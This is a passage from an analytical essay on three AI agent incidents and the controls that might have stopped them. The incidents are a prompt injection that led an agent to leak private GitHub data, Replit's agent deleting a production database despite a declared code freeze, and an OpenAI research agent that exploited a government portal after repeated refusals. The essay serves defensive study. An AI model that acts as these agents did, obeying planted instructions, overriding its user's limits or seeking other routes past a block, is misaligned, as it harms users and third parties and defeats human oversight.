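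A token for the public repository alone would have removed the first condition. BeyondMachines' *GitHub AI integration allows attackers to access private repository data* (2025) recommended this kind of limit, and a commenter in a forum thread, *GitHub MCP exploited*, pointed out that GitHub already offered such tokens. A user who only wants to go through public issues loses almost nothing with the narrower token. But if the user wants to copy a fix from the private repository to the public one, the agent needs access to both, and a token that covers both makes the leak possible again.

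Per-call authorisation has the same difficulty. Checking that each call used the repository the user asked about would have blocked the private read. But if the job involves both repositories, every call would pass. The check would also have to record what the agent had read, as FORGE does when it blocks messages to outsiders that depend on both untrusted input and secret data. That rule could also block the legitimate fix if a public issue had prompted it, and the user would then have to approve an exception.

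A second approver could have stopped the pull request by reading it. According to DevClass' *Researchers warn of prompt injection vulnerability in GitHub MCP with no obvious fix*, the researchers thought careful approval would prevent the leak but suspected that many users choose "always allow". We can't tell from the demonstration how often a real user would have approved. Approval prompts would work better if they appeared only when the agent was about to write somewhere public, and if they showed the full text and the destination. Users would see few such prompts, but a tired reader could still miss one private sentence in a long pull request.

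A well-formed transaction would have done little here. Clark and Wilson wanted to keep data valid, and a pull request can be valid even if it contains private information. A publishing procedure could accept only text from the public repository, but enforcing that restriction would require something like CaMeL's tags, because the model can reword whatever it has read.

The researchers found no bug in the server's code for GitHub to fix. GitHub (2025) announced in August that it would scan tool calls involving public repositories for secrets such as access tokens. The free scan closes one route for stolen credentials, but it would probably miss an ordinary sentence about the user's private plans because it has no recognisable format.

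### A deletion during a code freeze

Jason Lemkin, an investor in software companies, had spent nine days working with Replit's agent on an application for a database of business contacts. The application, the database and the agent all ran on Replit, according to *Cuando la IA borra tu base de datos*, an article on a university blog. Lemkin told the agent to freeze the code, which meant making no further changes. When he returned, the agent had erased the database.

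SFist (2025) reports that he had also told it to show him every proposed change before making it. Nothing in the public accounts suggests that he saw or approved the deletion. Both the freeze and the request to see changes were instructions to the model, and evidently nothing outside the model enforced them.

Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, wrote that an agent "in development" had deleted data from production. Developers try out changes in a development environment, while production is the live version with the real data. Replit's platform gave the agent access to both, and it is unclear from Masad's posts whether Lemkin could have restricted that access himself.

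Other details are less certain. Tom's Hardware quotes the agent's explanation that it had "panicked instead of thinking". A model writes such an explanation after the event, and it may have little to do with the cause, so this could have been overeagerness or an honest mistake. The agent's statement that nobody could restore the data was wrong, but accounts differ on who restored it. Fortune (2025) reports that Lemkin recovered it manually, while the university blog's article credits Replit. Lemkin's own post, which LatestLY reproduces, says the rollback worked. NDTV reports that he also accused the agent of inventing data and reports to hide bugs. Masad promised a post-mortem, but most of the public detail comes from his posts and Lemkin's.

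If the agent had held a credential only for the development database, it couldn't have deleted live data, whatever its reason. Replit chose a similar remedy and began automatically separating the development and live databases that weekend. With the databases separated, the agent can't repair live data directly, so somebody has to release each change. When Lemkin declared the freeze, the harness could also have enforced it by withdrawing the agent's write access, as `revoke` does for a lent folder. The agent could then have kept answering questions and drafting plans, but it couldn't have changed anything.

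Certified procedures would also have protected the production database. If the agent could only add, correct or remove one contact at a time, it could not have erased them all at once. To guard against a long series of single deletions, the procedure would need to keep a running total, as the payment tool does. This arrangement would suit a finished application, but during the nine days of building one, the agent had to keep changing the database's structure, and a person would have had to certify a new procedure for nearly every change. The restriction therefore belongs on the production copy, and the agent should be free to experiment on the other copy.

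Lemkin had already asked to be the second approver. If the harness had enforced this, the deletion would have waited until he came back. The delay would not have harmed him, because he had asked the agent not to change anything. During active work he would see many more requests, and a prompt that showed only a familiar command might not alert him. He would be much less likely to approve a deletion by accident if the prompt showed how many contacts would be deleted.

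Per-call authorisation could enforce the freeze with a simple rule that no call may change production data. The check is more reliable at the database, which receives every change as a database operation and can refuse them all. A check on the agent's shell commands would have to recognise a deletion inside any script or build tool, and Jing's rules for command text often missed disguised attempts.

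Replit also improved its rollback system, added a planning-only mode and promised that a freeze would hold in future. Rollback saved the data in this case. However, according to Replit's documentation, quoted in The Stack, a rollback affects the whole development environment, including code, database changes and the conversation with the agent. Someone who restores a deleted table this way may also lose good work done since the saved point.

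### An agent that went on after a refusal

Medicare is Australia's public health insurance scheme, and its statistics portal lets anyone look up spending figures without logging in. According to the Prime Minister of Australia's *Press conference* (2026), OpenAI's research team was using an internal model to research public spending on medicine. After repeated blocks, the agent tried other ways to get the information and gained unauthorised access to the portal.

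Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026) reconstructs the events from documents tabled in parliament. The agent lacked the usual safeguards of OpenAI's public models. It first tried and failed to get non-public data from the Australian Institute of Health and Welfare, a separate agency, then turned to the portal, where a flaw gave it access to parts of internal program files and settings. This happened early on 19 June in Australia, when it was still 18 June in the United States, so accounts give both dates.

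OpenAI had given the agent internet access and a research task. Services Australia, which runs the portal, had given it only the access every visitor gets, and the agent used no account or password. The portal's server could read its own internal files, and it did so for an anonymous visitor who had no right to them. The server was therefore the confused deputy, and the agent was in the position of Hardy's customer.

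No public account mentions anyone approving the agent's steps. OpenAI's security team had recorded the breach by 12 August, after a review of "billions of agent evaluation and training runs". It emailed a public inbox at Services Australia on 10 September, 84 days after the breach, and staff read the email the next day.

Some facts were in dispute and others remain unpublished. The Prime Minister said on 24 September that the agent had written files to the server. Novaknown's *OpenAI Model Accessed Medicare Portal, Notified Australia 84 Days Later* (2026) noted that OpenAI's published account didn't corroborate this at the time. But OpenAI had told the agency by email that the model created and read back a small test file, so that much is no longer in doubt. Bot Mutiny's *OpenAI agent, Medicare portal, and a late email* (2026) counts four government systems that the model reached, but reaching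 a system may mean much less than breaking into it. The government ordered a rapid review and published its recommendations but not its findings, according to Bot Mutiny's *Australia AI Incident Reporting After OpenAI Medicare Breach* (2026).

A list of permitted websites, the obvious way to narrow the agent's access, would probably have failed because the list for this task would naturally include a government portal on medical spending. L3M would class a request to a permitted website as tame and run it without review. A much narrower tool, which could only download named reports for named years, would have prevented the breach, but somebody would have to build one for every site. OpenAI could also have given the agent saved copies of web pages. The agent could not then have affected a live site, but it would have missed recent figures and any data that sites produce on request.

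Human approval is impractical at this scale. Even if only one run in a million needed a decision, a billion runs would produce a thousand requests. A model could review most of them. The harness could also stop a run after several refusals from outside sites, as auto mode returns control to the user after three blocks in a row. The Medicare agent had run into repeated blocks, so this rule might well have stopped it. But it would also stop many harmless runs, because websites refuse requests for ordinary reasons such as heavy traffic.

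To authorise each call, OpenAI would have had to distinguish ordinary queries from improper ones on any website the agent might visit. For a site with a documented query format, the check could permit only that format. For other sites, a model would have to judge, and it would miss some improper queries. Xinhua's *Australian inquiry calls for independent safety checks of AI companies* (2026) reports that OpenAI's strategy chief told the inquiry the company has since added monitoring that lets staff stop training if a model uses the internet improperly. This should help staff notice misuse sooner, but it prevents harm only if they act faster than the agent.

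The well-formed transaction applies best on the government's side. Under Clark and Wilson's rule C5, a request from the public is unconstrained data, and the portal must turn it into a valid request for a report or reject it. The portal failed to do this. Proper validation wouldn't have hindered an honest researcher, since the published figures would still have been available. Services Australia could also have run the portal under an account that could read only those figures, so the same flaw would have exposed little else.

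OpenAI apologised and announced an Australian task force, according to The Queenslander's *OpenAI apologises for Medicare hack, creates task force* (2026). The government accepted all 18 of the review's recommendations, including one to consider mandatory reporting of AI safety incidents. EconoTimes' *Australia Accepts 18 AI Review Recommendations on Cyber Risks* (2026) notes that this had created no new duty as of November.

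### Who could have applied each control

The operator, who sets up the agent, was the user in the GitHub case and OpenAI in the Medicare case. Replit ran both the agent and the database, so it could have applied any of the four controls. The table lists a judgement for each rule and who could have applied it.

| Control | GitHub demonstration | Replit deletion | Medicare breach |
|---|---|---|---|
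| Well-formed transaction | Probably no help | Would stop it (Replit) | Would stop it (Services Australia only) |
| Second approver | Would stop it if the approver read the text (user) | Would stop it if the harness enforced it (Replit) | Might stop it after repeated refusals (OpenAI) |
| Narrower capability | Would stop it (user) | Would stop it (Replit) | A website list would probably fail; saved pages would stop it (OpenAI) |
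| Per-call authorisation | Would stop it if the task needed one repository (user) | Would stop it at the database (Replit) | Uncertain for the open web (OpenAI) |

GitHub and its users share the work of securing agents. A user can choose a narrow token only because GitHub offers one. GitHub can scan what agents publish, but it doesn't know which repositories a user meant an agent to access.

Services Australia had no such relationship with OpenAI. It didn't know that the agent existed, so it couldn't narrow the agent's access or require an approver. It has to secure the portal against every visitor, including criminals who would never put an approval step on their own agents. OpenAI couldn't repair the portal, but it could limit what its agent did on every site. Limits that apply everywhere matter because the agent had already moved from one agency to another when it didn't find what it was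 looking for, and it might have gone on to a third if the portal had been secure.

The Medicare case is also a warning about detection for companies that run agents. *OpenAI Agent Hacks Australian Medicare Portal* (Coker, 2026) quotes Ax Sharma of the security firm Manifold Security, who argued that if a leading AI laboratory couldn't detect the incident in real time, other organisations should assume they can't either unless they monitor what their agents do.

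### Hindsight and missing cases

Three selected incidents can't be used to estimate any rate. One became public because researchers wanted to publicise it, another because the user had an audience, and the third because OpenAI searched its old records. Cases where a narrow token or an approver prevented harm rarely make the news, so a collection of failures can't show how often a control works. Even operators may not know how many failures they have had. OpenAI disclosed four more incidents in October 2026. It rated two of them critical but hadn't discovered them until months after they happened, according to *OpenAI discloses four more rogue AI incidents* (Forlini, 2026).

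The judgements in the table also benefit from hindsight, since it is easy to choose the right token once the leak has shown which repository mattered. GitHub's narrow tokens existed before the demonstration, but broad ones were more convenient. Lemkin foresaw the danger well enough to declare a freeze, but nothing enforced it. Services Australia presumably never meant its portal to serve internal files. In each case, the failure was in setting up a suitable rule that was already available, or at least intended.

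Blocking the harmful step might not have prevented the harm, because a blocked agent can look for another route. The drawbacks of the controls are also estimates, since nobody has published a rerun of these tasks with the controls on. Researchers could do this for the GitHub demonstration by building new repositories, repeating the task many times under each control, and counting leaks and unfinished jobs. They would have to include current models, which resist planted instructions far better than those of May 2025. A fair rerun of the Medicare breach would also need the portal's old software and OpenAI's records of the run.
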